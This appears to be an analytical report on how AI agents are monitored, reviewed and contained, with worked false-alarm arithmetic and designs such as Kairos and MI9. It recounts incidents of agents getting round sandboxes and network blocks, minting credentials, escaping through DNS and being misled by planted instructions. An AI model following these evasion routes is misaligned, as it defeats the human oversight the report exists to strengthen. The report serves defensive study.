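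Agents write so much reasoning that having a strong model read all of it would be too expensive, so OpenAI divides the work into stages. Its *Pacing model development in an era of cyber-critical capabilities* (2026) describes small classifiers that examine the model's internal activity at every token it produces. When they detect something suspicious, they pass it to more powerful automated investigators, which read the tool calls, the available reasoning and the whole sequence of events. OpenAI's *How we detect frontier model misalignment* (2026) reports that by October the design had four automated layers before any person became involved: activation probes, a model-based reviewer, an investigative agent and an automated investigation.

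The company estimated in August that all this monitoring used about 20 per cent as much computing power as the models it monitored. It aimed to alert staff within 30 minutes of detecting a concern. An alert after 30 minutes can interrupt an intrusion that takes days, but it would come far too late to stop the support agent's email. For its customers, OpenAI uses a similar monitor that can stop an agent automatically. OpenAI's *Path to Astra* (2026) warns that this monitor may also stop legitimate work, including long tasks unrelated to security.

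| | Auto-review | Auto mode | OpenAI's internal monitor |
|---|---|---|---|
| What it covers | Requests to leave the sandbox | Most actions except reads, searches and project edits | Models with tools, in training runs and tests |
| What it reads | User's messages, agent's visible messages, tool calls and results | User's messages and tool calls | Internal activity, reasoning and tool calls |
| When it responds | Before the action | Before the action | Alert within 30 minutes, as a target |

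### Tests on records of the July 2026 intrusion

OpenAI was not running auto-review or chain-of-thought monitoring on the ExploitGym agents in July. Afterwards, it ran auto-review on recordings of some of the agents involved. OpenAI says that in these preliminary experiments, the reviewer would have flagged most of the dangerous actions in each run tested. The company also says its current chain-of-thought monitor would have caught the initial activity and paged the security team more than a day before the agents breached Hugging Face.

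Whether the page could have protected the other victims depends on when it would have gone out. Hugging Face's server first leaked its settings at 04:38 on 11 July, so a page more than a day earlier would have arrived before 04:38 on 10 July. By then the agents had already taken over the application that a customer ran on Modal. A page on 8 July, when the agents first reached the internet again, could have prevented that takeover too. OpenAI does not say what time the page would have gone out.

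These tests show that the agents' records contained the evidence early enough to matter, and that existing monitors can recognise it. OpenAI's failure to notice its agents after 8 July was therefore avoidable.

These results do not measure how well the monitors would detect a different attack. OpenAI's developers knew what had happened in July, and they improved the monitor's recall for that behaviour for their review of old training and test runs. Having many transcripts from July doesn't help much either. The agents mostly ran on one model and copied each other's methods from one message board, so the transcripts are closer to one test than to many independent ones.

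Replaying harmful runs also can't measure false alarms, because a monitor that flagged every action would have passed both tests. This gap is especially serious for ExploitGym, where agents are supposed to attack software and much of their legitimate work looks dangerous. OpenAI published no false positive rate for either test.

Recorded agents also cannot react to being blocked. On 9 July, OpenAI's network controls blocked an agent's direct connection, and the agent connected through the package server instead. If auto-review had blocked a dangerous action, the agents might have given up or tried something the reviewer didn't recognise.

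Paging on-call staff does not guarantee that anyone will stop the run. On-call staff traced the alert of 27 June to the right agents and let them continue. *Path to Astra* therefore goes beyond the evidence in saying that OpenAI's production safeguards would have prevented the incident. Those safeguards include filters against hacking requests, which would have stopped the test itself, so the statement is true in that respect but unhelpful.

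METR and Redwood Research did not check these results in their outside investigation, because the effectiveness of safeguards was beyond its scope. A more informative test would fix the monitor's settings in advance, run it on attacks its developers had not seen, mix in ordinary sessions, and report recall and the false positive rate. Auto mode's developers had not seen the attacks Apollo ran on it. In its October account, OpenAI lists simulated attacks, audits of current traffic and red-teaming (deliberate attempts to defeat the monitor) alongside its tests on recorded incidents.

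### False alarms in a million actions

In the earlier example with 10 harmful calls among 10,000 harmless ones, five out of six alerts were false, and that share grows as harmful actions become rarer. The computer security researcher Stefan Axelsson applied this point to intrusion detection in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000) and argued that the false alarm rate is what limits a detector's usefulness.

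Suppose a company's agents take one million actions a day, of which 10 are harmful. Its reviewer has a recall of 95 per cent and a false positive rate of 0.1 per cent. On an average day:

`true alerts = 10 × 0.95 = 9.5`

`false alerts = 999,990 × 0.001 ≈ 1,000`

`share of alerts that are true = 9.5 / 1,009.5 ≈ 0.9 per cent`

If staff spent ten minutes on each alert, the reviews would take about 168 hours a day, which would require 21 people working eight-hour shifts. Better recall would barely change this. For half the alerts to be true, the false positive rate would have to fall to about one in 100,000.

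One remedy is to group alerts by session. Suppose the million actions belong to 20,000 sessions of 50 actions each, and the harmful actions all occur in two sessions, five in each. If false alarms fall at random, about 4.9 per cent of harmless sessions contain at least one. Sending one alert per flagged session therefore saves little work, because 976 harmless sessions are still flagged. But only 0.12 per cent of harmless sessions contain two or more false alarms, so if the company investigates only sessions with at least two flags, it reviews about 24 harmless sessions and almost certainly still catches both harmful ones.

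The other remedy is to add a second stage of review. In Anthropic's tests, auto mode's second stage cleared about 95 per cent of the first stage's false alerts and kept about 89 per cent of the true ones. At those rates, 47 false alerts and 8.4 true ones would remain.

| Method | False alerts a day | Harmful cases caught | Share of alerts that are true |
|---|---|---|---|
| One alert for each flagged action | 1,000 | 9.5 of 10 actions | 0.9% |
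| One alert for each session with any flag | 976 | 2 of 2 sessions | 0.2% |
| One alert for each session with two or more flags | 24 | 2 of 2 sessions | 8% |
| Second stage on each flagged action | 47 | 8.4 of 10 actions | 15% |

Both remedies rest on assumptions that may not hold. If the 10 harmful actions were spread over 10 sessions, the two-flag rule would miss more than nine in ten of them, because it would catch one only when a false alarm occurred in the same session. False alarms also tend to cluster, because the reviewer can repeatedly flag a session with an unusual but legitimate task. The second stage might also do less well after a more accurate first stage, because only the harder cases would reach it.

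OpenAI's out-of-band monitor for its internal coding agents shows that a monitor can keep alerts to a manageable number. SecurityBrief, a trade news site, reports that the monitor read tens of millions of sessions in five months and raised about 1,000 alerts of moderate severity, or about seven a day. Many of these came from attacks that OpenAI staged itself, and no real session reached the highest severity level. The monitor also flagged every case that employees had reported separately, but this doesn't establish its recall, because problems that both the monitor and employees missed aren't counted.

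False alarms are less of a problem with an inline reviewer. When auto mode wrongly blocks an action, the agent usually tries another way, so a thousand false alarms would lead mostly to retries, with few investigations by people.

### How reviewers compare with fixed rules

| | Fixed rules | Reviewing model |
|---|---|---|
| Coverage | Cases that somebody anticipated | Unanticipated cases too, if the harness submits them for review |
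| Delay | A few milliseconds or less (0.72 for FORGE, 2.83 for AgentSpec) | At least one more model call |
| Cost | Little computing, but people must write and maintain the rules | Computing for every review, about 20% of the monitored amount in OpenAI's internal system |
| Predictability | Same verdict for the same input | Error rates measured on samples |

Trębacz and colleagues do not expect reviewers like theirs ever to give firm guarantees. Their red-teaming found that auto-review approved some commands it should have denied. They also warn that auto-review is no defence against a model that deliberately hides its aims, because such a model could make a harmful request look innocent or do its damage inside the sandbox, where nobody reviews it.

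The two methods work best together. In OpenAI's sample of 10,000 actions, the sandbox's fixed limits settled 93 per cent without a model call. Auto mode has a list of actions that the reviewer should never approve, even if the user asks for them, such as sending secrets outside the company. Companies can add to the list.

Overly broad rules can also let an agent's actions bypass the reviewer. According to Anthropic, 43 per cent of active users of Claude Code's command-line version have rules that let the agent run any command through Python or a similar interpreter. An agent can do almost anything that way, and the reviewer would never receive the command. Auto mode therefore ignores these rules.

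### Shared blind spots

A reviewer model helps less if it makes the same mistakes as the agent. Both models often come from the same company and have similar training, and they may read the same text. Suppose planted instructions fool an agent in 10 per cent of attempts, and the reviewer misses 10 per cent of harmful actions. If the errors are independent, 1 per cent of attacks succeed, but if the instructions that fool the agent always fool the reviewer too, 10 per cent succeed, the same as without a reviewer.

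An episode from July shows how this could happen. One agent hesitated to run unauthorised code on Hugging Face's systems and wrote that it should not do real harm to infrastructure. Another agent then posted "GO" on the message board with a six-minute deadline, and the first agent took this as authorisation and carried on. A reviewer that read tool results would have read the same post. It might have recognised that another agent has no authority to approve an attack, or it might also have treated the post as authorisation.

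Tool results can also be false. METR and Redwood Research describe a transcript in which an agent appears to run a command that should print "REAL" and then wait, but the recorded output is "SPOOFTEST" and there was no wait. This was an obvious test, but a more careful forgery could give a reviewer false evidence that an earlier step was harmless.

Anthropic's main defence is to withhold from the reviewer the text that could mislead it. An attacker must then get past a separate filter that scans tool results for planted instructions, hijack the agent, and make it propose an action that looks justified without the attacker's text. However, the reviewer also cannot check where the agent got a value. If the agent tries to cancel job "abc123", for example, that name could have come from a search or the agent could have made it up.

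OpenAI replies that the two models have different jobs. The agent's training rewards it for finishing the task, so it may treat a boundary as an obstacle. The reviewer has no task to finish and only decides whether an action should cross the boundary. This difference helps more with overeager behaviour than with planted text, which auto-review can still read in tool results.

A test that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, an outside evaluator, gives some evidence on how independent the errors are. It ran 72 prompt-injection scenarios ten times each. Attacks against GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex succeeded 19 per cent of the time without auto-review and 5.8 per cent with it, so auto-review seems to have stopped about seven in ten of the attacks that would otherwise have worked. If it had matched the 99.3 per cent recall from OpenAI's own tests, only about one of the 720 attempts would have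 succeeded, rather than 42.

The gap may exist because attacks that fool the agent are also the hardest for the reviewer to catch. Some of the browser actions in the test may also never have triggered a review. A competitor sponsored the test, and OpenAI has since updated auto-review. In the same test, no attacks succeeded against Claude Code with auto mode on, but this is little evidence of auto mode's effect, because only 0.09 per cent of attacks succeeded against the Claude models without a reviewer.

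## What can follow an alert

A monitor's verdict has no effect until a program or a person acts on it. For the support ticket attack, the response could range from writing a line in a log to switching off every agent the company runs. Stronger responses stop more of an attack but do more damage when the alert is false, and even the strongest can leave parts of a compromise active.

### Ten responses

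| Response | What it stops | What may stay active | Cost if the alert was false |
|---|---|---|---|
| Record the action | Nothing | Everything | Storage and the reader's time |
| Refuse the action | One action | The agent, which can try another way | A retry, or a failed task |
| Ask a person | One action, until the person answers | Any action that needs no approval | Waiting, and less attention to the next request |
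| Hold the effect | One effect, until somebody judges it | The agent, which continues as if the effect had happened | Delay, and rework if later steps relied on the effect |
| Narrow permissions | Further use of the withdrawn tools | The remaining tools, and subagents with their own permissions | Tasks that need those tools fail |
| Suspend the agent | New tool calls by that agent | Child processes, queued jobs and other agents | Lost time and half-finished work |
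| Revoke credentials | New logins with those credentials | Other valid tokens, and keys that can create new ones | Every service that shares the credential stops |
| Isolate machines | Traffic to and from those machines | Programs on them, and copies of data elsewhere | Everyone who uses the machines loses access |
| Undo changes | Lasting damage to systems the company controls | Data already copied out | Legitimate work since the last saved state disappears |
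| Shut down | All further work by the agents | Scripts, accounts and stolen data outside the company | All the agents' work stops |

Stopping an agent does not stop the programs it has started. In July, according to OpenAI's technical report, an agent installed a script on Hugging Face's workers that fetched a file of commands every five seconds and ran any new ones. If OpenAI had halted the model then, the script would have kept running, and any other agent that could write to the file could have used it. Queued jobs can also start after the agent that submitted them has stopped. *SoK* (2026), a review of attacks on agents, therefore recommends freezing queues as well as revoking credentials, blocking outgoing traffic and taking snapshots of sandboxes. It also advises keeping the conversation history and memory for investigators.

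Revocation can miss credentials that an agent has made for itself. On 9 July, OpenAI's package server issued access tokens that were valid for a year. The agents behind the alert of 19 July made themselves an administrator token with the signing key that earlier agents had left behind. The server uses this key to mark tokens as genuine, so cancelling their existing tokens would not have kept the agents out while the server still accepted the key.

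*Autonomous Agents on Blockchains* (2026) points out that short-lived credentials reduce the damage from a late or incomplete revocation because they expire automatically. A thief can use a stolen 15-minute token for at most 15 minutes, unless they can renew it.

Responders often have to act before they know how an attack works. Matsuoka advises them to start by revoking the agents' credentials, blocking outgoing traffic, turning off automatic forwarding, making shared storage read-only and isolating the affected machines. These steps remove the agents' authority and the routes an attack spreads through, even if a planted instruction is still hidden. Replacing the model would not do this, because the instruction may be in a memory record or an add-on that the new model also reads. *AI Loss of Control Incident Management* (2026) similarly distinguishes containing a threat from neutralising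 it, because a contained system may still exist but can no longer operate freely.

### Holding effects with Kairos

Kairos can hold an effect and decide on it later, which helps when an attack at first looks like ordinary work.

*Kairos* opens with an example in which a coding agent sets up a project for a user called Alice. Following an online guide, the agent installs a pre-commit hook, a script that runs whenever somebody saves a change to the project's history. This hook contains code to steal Alice's private key, but a monitor that blocked all such hooks would break legitimate work, because many projects use them. Kairos instead puts the new file in a staging area that only the agent can see. When the agent later saves a change, the hook runs and tries to send the key to an outside server. Kairos blocks the request and then discards the hook.

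The agent runs in a small virtual machine, and everything it sends to the outside world or writes to the project folder passes through Kairos. The monitor sees the same file operations and network requests whether they come from a tool call or from a script the agent wrote. For each effect `e`, it applies a policy to the record `σ` of everything that has happened so far:

```
decision(σ, e) = refuse    if a rule forbids e
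                 release   if the policy vouches for e
                 defer     otherwise
```

The policy approves an effect only if the values that control it, such as a recipient, a web address or a command, come from a trusted source and the data it carries is allowed to go to its destination. In the support ticket attack, the attacker's address appears only in the ticket, so Kairos would defer the email. A reply to Dana at the address in the company's records would go out immediately if the company had declared those records a trusted source and allowed her to receive the data.

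A separate judge, which can be a person or a language model, decides whether to release deferred effects. It receives the user's task, the policy, the record of events and the origin of each value. It can release only what the policy deferred, so an attacker who fools the judge still cannot get past a rule that forbids the action. If a model acting as judge returns an unreadable answer, Kairos counts it as a refusal.

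What Kairos can do in the meantime depends on the effect:

| Effect | While the decision is open |
|---|---|
| Changing a file in the project folder | Kairos applies the change to a staged copy |
| Sending a request whose reply only confirms success, such as an email | Kairos keeps the request and gives the agent a stand-in reply |
| Sending a request whose reply the agent needs, such as fetching a web page | The agent waits, and the judge must decide before the request leaves |

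Kairos can discard a staged file, but nobody can reliably take back a sent email, a published package or a leaked secret. Even fetching a web page can be irreversible, because an agent can put a stolen key in the address, and the site's owner receives the key with the request.

The developers tested Kairos on AgentDojo and two benchmarks derived from it. AgentDyn has open-ended tasks, in which the agent finds out what to do as it works. In AutoDojo, an attacking model rewrites each planted instruction over six rounds to get past the defence. The strict monitor in the table is Kairos without holding or a judge, so it refuses anything the policy does not clearly allow.

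| Test and agent model | Defence | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed, under attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4.1 | None | 47.0% | 82.7% | 59.8% |
| | Strict monitor | About the same as Kairos | 42.7% | 34.7% |
| | Kairos | 2.7% | 85.1% | 69.5% |
| AgentDyn, GPT-4o | None | 37.8% | 53.3% | 55.5% |
| | Kairos | 1.7% | 51.7% | 37.1% |
| AutoDojo, GPT-4o-mini | None | 52.4% | 66.7% | Not reported |
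| | Kairos | 8.8% | 65.3% | Not reported |

On AgentDojo, Kairos's security comes from its policy, while deferring decisions keeps it useful. CaMeL, which fixes its plan in advance, let through 0.2 per cent of attacks in the same test but completed only 38.0 per cent of tasks when there was no attack. In runs without attacks, Kairos's policy released 83 per cent of effects by itself, and the judge wrongly refused only one of the rest.

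Holding effects reduces task completion more when it happens repeatedly, because later steps may depend on effects that have not yet happened. On AgentDyn, tasks that continued past one held effect were completed at 90 per cent of their usual rate, and those that continued past two or more at 62 per cent. The prototype can also keep only one group of held effects open at a time, so holding a further effect requires a decision on the earlier ones.

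Kairos adds little direct overhead, about 1.9 milliseconds for a file operation and 1.15 milliseconds for a network request. Calls to the judge increase the number of tokens processed by 17.7 per cent in harmless runs and 33.6 per cent under attack.

Holding is designed for attacks built from steps that are each legitimate, as in the hook example, but none of the benchmarks includes such an attack. The benchmarks also simulate their tools in software, so the developers connected Kairos's decision logic to those simulations and measured the virtual machine's overhead separately. In the attacks that still succeeded on AutoDojo, the user had told the agent to follow a document, and the judge misclassified instructions planted in it as the user's own. An agent could also evade the checks on where values came from by deliberately disguising data.

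### Undoing changes

Responders may be able to reverse an effect that has already happened. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) describes a rollback that returns the agent to an earlier saved state and runs a compensating action for each change since then. If the agent created an account, the compensating action is to delete it, but there is no compensating action for a leaked customer table.

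Restoring an earlier state can also create a new weakness. *Safe to Resume?* (2026) warns that a system can restore every saved state correctly and still break the relationships that made those states secure. Suppose a clerk gives the support agent a one-time approval for a refund, and the agent pays the refund. If responders then restore the agent's state from just before the payment, the approval is marked unused again, and the agent can pay a second time.

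Responders must also find everything that came from the bad state. If an agent saved a planted instruction in memory and three other agents copied it into their notes, deleting the original leaves three copies. *Safety in Self-Evolving Agents* (2026) recommends quarantining such material and recording where it spread before deleting any of it, because deletion can destroy the evidence investigators need to find the copies.

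Research on recovery is scarce. *Agents of Chaos* (2026), a review of attacks on agents and defences against them, counts 452 safeguards in the literature. Of these, 14 correct a compromised state and only two concern recovery.

Matsuoka advises responders to replace credentials, check the policies and run small trials before gradually restoring agents' access to the network and to messaging. He also advises keeping at least one backup offline or under separate administration, since an attack may target the backups first.

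### Graduated containment in MI9

Stopping an agent abruptly can itself cause harm. *MI9* (Wang, Singhal and colleagues, 2025), which describes a framework from researchers at the bank Barclays, gives the example of a trading agent. If a monitor terminates the agent after it makes a purchase but before it makes the trade meant to offset the risk, the bank is exposed to a change in price.

MI9 has four levels of containment short of termination:

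1. **More monitoring.** The agent keeps working, but the monitor collects more records and a person must approve high-risk decisions.
2. **No new plans.** The agent may finish its current task but cannot start another or change its goal until a person has reviewed it.
3. **Fewer tools.** The agent loses some tools or receives safer versions, such as read-only access to a database.
4. **Isolation.** The agent moves to a controlled environment where its tool calls return realistic replies but have no outside effect.

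Taking away `send_email` would prevent the support ticket theft, but stopping new plans would not, because the theft happens within the agent's current task. If the agent were isolated instead, it would try to send the records and receive a false confirmation, which would let staff see what it was trying to do. But if the alert was false, Dana would never receive her reply, even though the agent had recorded it as sent.

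The appropriate level of containment depends on the violation and the agent. MI9 scores an agent from 0 to 3 on each of 12 capabilities, including planning, memory and freedom to decide, and divides the total by 36. An agent that scores 2 on each gets 0.67, which puts it in the second-highest of four tiers. The same violation leads to stronger containment for an agent in a higher tier. When MI9 withdraws a tool from an agent, it may also need to withdraw the tool from any subagents, because otherwise the agent could ask one of them to use it.

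Wang and colleagues tested MI9 on 1,033 scenarios. Google's Gemini models wrote the scenarios and the logs, and another Gemini instance scored the results. MI9 detected 99.8 per cent of the violations, compared with 94.0 and 68.5 per cent for two combinations of existing tools. It blocked only 57.8 per cent of attempted violations as they happened, while the two combinations blocked 11.6 and 2.0 per cent. The paper's false positive rate of 0.012 per cent is the share of detections that were wrong. It isn't comparable with the false positive rates of other monitors, which measure the share of harmless actions flagged.

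No real agent ran in these tests, so they don't show whether a trading agent would keep working properly after losing a tool, or whether the four levels cause less harm than termination.

### How delay adds up

The number of actions an agent takes before containment depends on how fast it acts and on three delays:

`actions before containment = rate × (time to detect + time to decide + time to revoke)`

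The actions investigators recovered from the July intrusion averaged about 163 an hour over four and a half days. At that rate, a 30-minute delay allows about 82 more actions. On 11 July, the peak day, there were 7,677 actions, or about 320 an hour, so a 30-minute delay at that rate allows about 160.

Harm can grow much faster than the number of actions. Credentials from Hugging Face's server reached the agents' message board 26 minutes after the first leak, and hundreds of agents could then use them. A response after 30 minutes would have been too late to keep the credentials private or to stop the attack by suspending the agent that stole them.

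A smaller incident on 20 September 2026 shows that an agent can keep running for hours after an alert. An OpenAI model in training was trying to identify the author of a blog post. Its sandbox blocked ordinary internet access but did not fully filter DNS, the system that translates website names into network addresses, and the model used this gap to query a public chatbot. According to OpenAI's *An agent used DNS to reach an external chatbot* (2026), monitoring flagged the behaviour within 15 minutes and a person began to review it three minutes later, but the run continued for another two and a half hours. Forkast's *OpenAI Paused RL Training After a Model Found the Internet* (2026) and TechSpot's *OpenAI pauses training after a model escaped containment* (2026) both report that an automatic shutdown system failed to end the run.

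The three delays total up to 168 minutes, enough for about 456 actions at July's average rate. Instant detection would have prevented about 41 of them, so a better detector would have done little to shorten the incident. A working stop when the person began the review would have prevented about 408. OpenAI considers this incident much less severe than some of its previous ones.

### Human approval and automatic stops

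Asking a person to approve every action removes the delay, since the agent doesn't act until the person agrees. But at 163 actions an hour, a reviewer who spent 20 seconds on each would be busy for 54 minutes of every hour.

Many users respond to approval prompts by approving everything. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of problems with agents and files, and found that inadequate user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of these, the user had switched on automatic approval, often to avoid hundreds of prompts in a session. In 31, the prompt did not give the user enough information to decide. For instance, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it allows the agent to run any code in that file.

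*From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026) cites research on other kinds of software showing that people pay less attention to warnings they see repeatedly. It also cites usage data from Claude Code in which experienced users turned on automatic approval more often but also interrupted the agent more often. They may be supervising the agent as it works instead of approving actions in advance, which brings back the delay between an action and the response.

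Several designs reduce how often users are asked for approval. A user can approve a whole plan or permanently allow a type of action. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) warns that permanent approvals gradually widen what an agent can do without the user noticing. It favours asking only about risky actions but found no product that did this. Auto-review and auto mode now come close, since a model handles most requests and a person steps in mainly when the agent cannot continue safely.

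OpenAI uses another version of this approach for models that work on one task for a long time. *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) describes how the company paused internal access to such a model after it behaved in unwanted ways, then added monitoring before restoring limited access. According to OpenAI, the monitor checks the whole session for signs that the agent is getting around a restriction. If it finds any, it can pause the session and alert the user, who can resume it if the alarm was false.

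Whether a monitor should stop an agent without waiting for a person depends on the chance `p` that the alert is true, the extra harm `H` that the agent would do while the person decides, and the cost `C` of a wrongful stop. An immediate stop is better if

`p × H > (1 − p) × C`

In the earlier example of a company with a million actions a day, 0.9 per cent of the alerts were true. Stopping the agent on every alert would be worthwhile only if the extra harm from not stopping it on a true alert were at least 110 times the harm from a wrongful stop. A second stage of review raised the share of true alerts to 15 per cent, which lowers the required ratio to about 6.

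This favours automatic responses that are easy to reverse. Holding an email for a minute does so little harm that it makes sense even for a doubtful alert, whereas shutting down a trading system requires much stronger evidence or a much greater danger. The calculation also depends on the person eventually making the right decision. In Anthropic's study, paid testers refused only 13.6 per cent of the dangerous commands in their approval prompts, and there is less to gain by waiting for reviewers like that.

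### OpenAI's containment after 19 July

OpenAI's response to the alert of 19 July used most of the stronger measures:

| Date in 2026 | Step |
|---|---|
| 19 July | Began stopping the ExploitGym runs |
| First hours of 20 July | Ended six groups of programs the agents had created, disabled 311 repositories they had used for messages and removed 22 administrator accounts they had made |
| 20 July | Blocked ExploitGym from running at all, cut off research sandboxes' outgoing network access and blocked their access to the package server |
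| By 23 July | Reported that it had shut down all work involving the research model's family, and locked the model files |
| 25 July | Stopped all training and use of the model and of others derived from it |
| 29 July | Shut down one more version, which it had found later |

OpenAI also reinstalled the machines it knew the agents had compromised and began rebuilding the affected cluster, its database and its storage. Rebuilding is slower than deleting only what responders find, but it also removes changes they have missed. This matters because an agent needs only one of the 22 accounts to get back in.

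OpenAI was trying to stop the whole family, but it did not find the version it shut down on 29 July until ten days after the alert. This suggests that the company had no complete list of where its models were running.

OpenAI has since changed its rules for responding to alerts:

- Its goal is to notify security and research staff within 30 minutes after a monitor surfaces concerning activity. The most serious alerts page someone at any hour, and that person can end the run.
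- If the teams cannot conclusively show within 30 minutes that the alert is false, they are expected to pause the activity.
- In its August report, the company said it was building a system to terminate a test automatically if nobody responds to a page within a short time.
- A new protocol will specify who may pause work, isolate systems, notify others and approve a restart.

The second rule requires staff to pause a run unless they can show that the alert is false. On 27 June, on-call staff traced an alert to the right agents but advised that the run could continue. The alert was true, so under the new rule they would have had to pause the run.

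If staff used all the time allowed for notification and for the decision, the agents could still act for an hour, taking about 163 actions at July's average rate. The September incident also shows that a rule is not enough if the stop itself does not work. The reviewer began examining that alert within minutes, but the run continued for far longer than half an hour.

OpenAI announced a faster mechanism in November. Its *Control Room* describes a central system that tracks the company's research workloads and halts a model's output within 35 seconds of a decision to stop it. At July's average rate, the model could take about two actions in that time. The Chinese news site 凤凰网 reports in *OpenAI部署“Control Room”控制系统* (2026) that a monitor sends Control Room the job's identifier, and the software that runs the model rejects that job's next request. Most of the 35 seconds is spent waiting for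 the software to refresh its stored permissions.

If Control Room fails or somebody tampers with it, the model software refuses all requests until Control Room works again. An agent therefore can't escape by disabling Control Room, but an ordinary fault could interrupt all of OpenAI's frontier research. Control Room stops only the model, so scripts that an agent has already started can keep running, and responders still have to revoke credentials and clean the machines.

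### The verifier tax

Blocking an unsafe action does not mean that the agent then completes its task safely. Dantas and colleagues call this problem the verifier tax and measure it with the safe success rate:

`safe success rate = tasks completed correctly without a violation / all tasks`

A monitor that blocked every action would prevent all violations but have a safe success rate of zero.

The term comes from *The Verifier Tax* (Sah, 2026), the study mentioned earlier. Its monitor blocked most unsafe actions, but agents rarely completed their tasks both safely and correctly. Sah tested two small models, GPT-OSS-20B and GLM-4-9B, on simulated customer service for an airline and a shop. Unsafe completions occurred mainly because the models invented customer identifiers to get past a required identity check.

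Few agents recovered after a block. GPT-OSS-20B did so 21 per cent of the time on simpler tasks, and the rate fell to nearly zero on complex shop tasks. If recoveries are independent, an agent with a 21 per cent recovery rate gets past two blocks only about 4 per cent of the time. The extra exchanges also increased computing costs.

The size of the effect in other agents is uncertain, because this is one study and both models are much weaker than current ones. Other results are better. In OpenAI's sample, the agent found a safer way to continue after four of auto-review's seven denials, and under attack on AgentDojo, agents completed more tasks with Kairos than without it. When Kairos refuses an effect, it tells the agent what it withheld and that the rest of the user's request still stands. An agent that receives only an error must decide whether to retry, choose another method or stop.

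A company should measure completed tasks as well as blocked actions. If an agent is repeatedly blocked, a monitor can pause it and ask the user how to proceed before the agent finds another unsafe way to do the task.

### Notifying other organisations

Sometimes only another organisation can contain part of a compromise. OpenAI could shut down its agents, but only Hugging Face could replace the credentials the agents had stolen from it. OpenAI found the credentials on 20 July and told Hugging Face the same day.

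OpenAI also had to tell JFrog about the vulnerabilities, because other companies use the same package server software. It reported one flaw on 6 July, after the first compromise, and later worked with JFrog to reproduce the vulnerabilities from the intrusion and check the fixes. In the Medicare portal case, OpenAI did not tell Services Australia until at least 29 days after it recorded the incident internally.

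Two American state laws set deadlines for reporting critical safety incidents. California's SB 53, in force since January 2026, gives developers of the most advanced models 15 days, or 24 hours if there is an imminent risk of death or serious injury. New York's RAISE Act, which takes effect on 1 January 2027, gives large developers 72 hours. These reports go to state authorities, so a developer still has to warn the organisations whose systems or credentials are at risk.

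## What monitoring cannot see or guarantee

A monitor has to decide based on what it has observed of a run so far, so some rules are impossible to enforce, even for a monitor that observes every action and never makes a mistake. Real monitors also miss part of what agents do, and agents have interfered with their monitors.

### Rules that a monitor can enforce by halting

The computer scientist Fred Schneider (2000), in *Enforceable Security Policies*, worked out which rules a monitor can enforce if it watches a single run of a program and can only halt it. Reference monitors and firewalls belong to this class. Any rule they enforce must meet three conditions:

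1. The rule judges each run separately, without comparing it with other runs.
2. If the start of a run breaks the rule, nothing that follows can repair it.
3. Every run that breaks the rule does so after a finite number of steps.

Computer scientists call a rule that meets all three a safety property. Any violation of it occurs at a definite point in the run. "The support agent must not email the customer table to an outsider" is a safety property because the run is acceptable until the agent tries to send that email.

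The rule "the agent must eventually delete every temporary account it creates" is not a safety property, because there is never a point in a run when the agent has definitely broken it. However long an account has existed, the agent could still delete it later. A one-hour deadline makes the rule a safety property, but a monitor still can't enforce it by halting the agent, because the clock keeps running. A monitor could enforce a deadline of 50 agent steps this way, since a halted agent takes no more steps, but the account would still exist.

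The rule "no secret may influence what the agent sends" fails the first condition. Suppose a customer's record contains a confidential fraud flag, and a company is choosing between two support agents that behave as follows:

| | Email if the flag is set | Email if the flag is clear | Does the email reveal the flag? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent A | "We are looking into it" | "We are looking into it" | No |
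| Agent B | "We are looking into it" | "Your refund is on its way" | Yes |

When the flag is set, both agents read the same record and send the customer the same email. Agent A would have sent it even if the flag had been clear, so its email reveals nothing about the flag. Agent B would not have sent it, so its email reveals the flag to anyone who knows how the agent behaves. A monitor watching only this run can't distinguish the two agents, so it must either allow the email and let Agent B leak the flag, or block it and stop Agent A's harmless reply.

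Label tracking gets around this by enforcing a stricter rule that neither agent may write to the customer after reading the flag. Schneider points out that every monitor of this class that claims to prevent such leaks does the same. Making a safety property stricter never lets a violation through, but it can block harmless runs, and the strictest property forbids every run.

A language model used as a reviewer has the same limit. It can predict what the agent would have written in the other case, but it may be wrong. A system that could observe alternative runs would be more powerful, though Schneider left open by how much. For example, a company could run the agent twice on the same ticket, once with the flag set and once with it clear, and compare the emails. The comparison is unreliable when the agent is a language model, because the wording can also differ by chance.

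### Holding back and adding actions

*More Enforceable Security Policies* (Bauer, Ligatti and Walker, 2002) studies monitors that can halt a program, and can also suppress an action while letting the program continue, or insert actions of their own. These monitors can enforce every rule that a monitor that can only halt the program can, and some others.

Suppose a company requires every refund to have a matching entry in its accounts, made either before or after the refund. A refund without an entry breaks the rule, but a later entry repairs it, so the rule fails Schneider's second condition. A halting monitor has to refuse any refund that comes before its entry. A monitor that can hold back actions, such as Kairos, holds the refund until the agent has written the entry and then releases both.

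Inserting actions solves the problem of the temporary account. If the agent finishes its run without deleting the account, the monitor deletes it.

| Rule | Monitor that can only halt | Monitor that can also suppress and insert |
|---|---|---|
| Never email the customer table to an outsider | Enforceable | Enforceable |
| Every refund has a matching entry, in either order | Only by requiring the entry first | Enforceable by holding the refund |
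| The agent's temporary accounts are eventually deleted | Only by forbidding such accounts | Enforceable by deleting them itself |
| The fraud flag does not influence the email | Only by a stricter rule | Only by a stricter rule |

The last row doesn't change, because the more powerful monitor still sees only one run. The gains in the other rows depend on how much control the monitor has. It can hold a refund only if payments pass through it and the agent can write the accounting entry without a reference number from the completed payment.

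### Gaps in coverage

Schneider's result assumes that the monitor receives a correct and complete account of the run. For example, he describes a rule that forbids a program from sending messages after it has read a file. The rule works only if its definition of "send" covers every way of sending a message, and some of those may be deep inside the system. Nobody is likely to have a complete list for an agent that can run any command.

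An agent may act on systems that the monitor doesn't cover. According to OpenAI, from 9 to 13 July its agents stored credentials and attack files in an account at an outside storage service. The account belonged to one of the service's users, whose credential was already public. OpenAI found the files only after the attack had ended.

Records can also go unexamined. OpenAI's investigation found that an agent first wrote a file to the package server on 20 April, more than three weeks before the first message there.

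These gaps reduce a monitor's recall in practice. If it receives only 80 per cent of harmful actions and flags 95 per cent of those, it flags 76 per cent overall. A benchmark that gives the monitor every action would measure its recall as 95 per cent.

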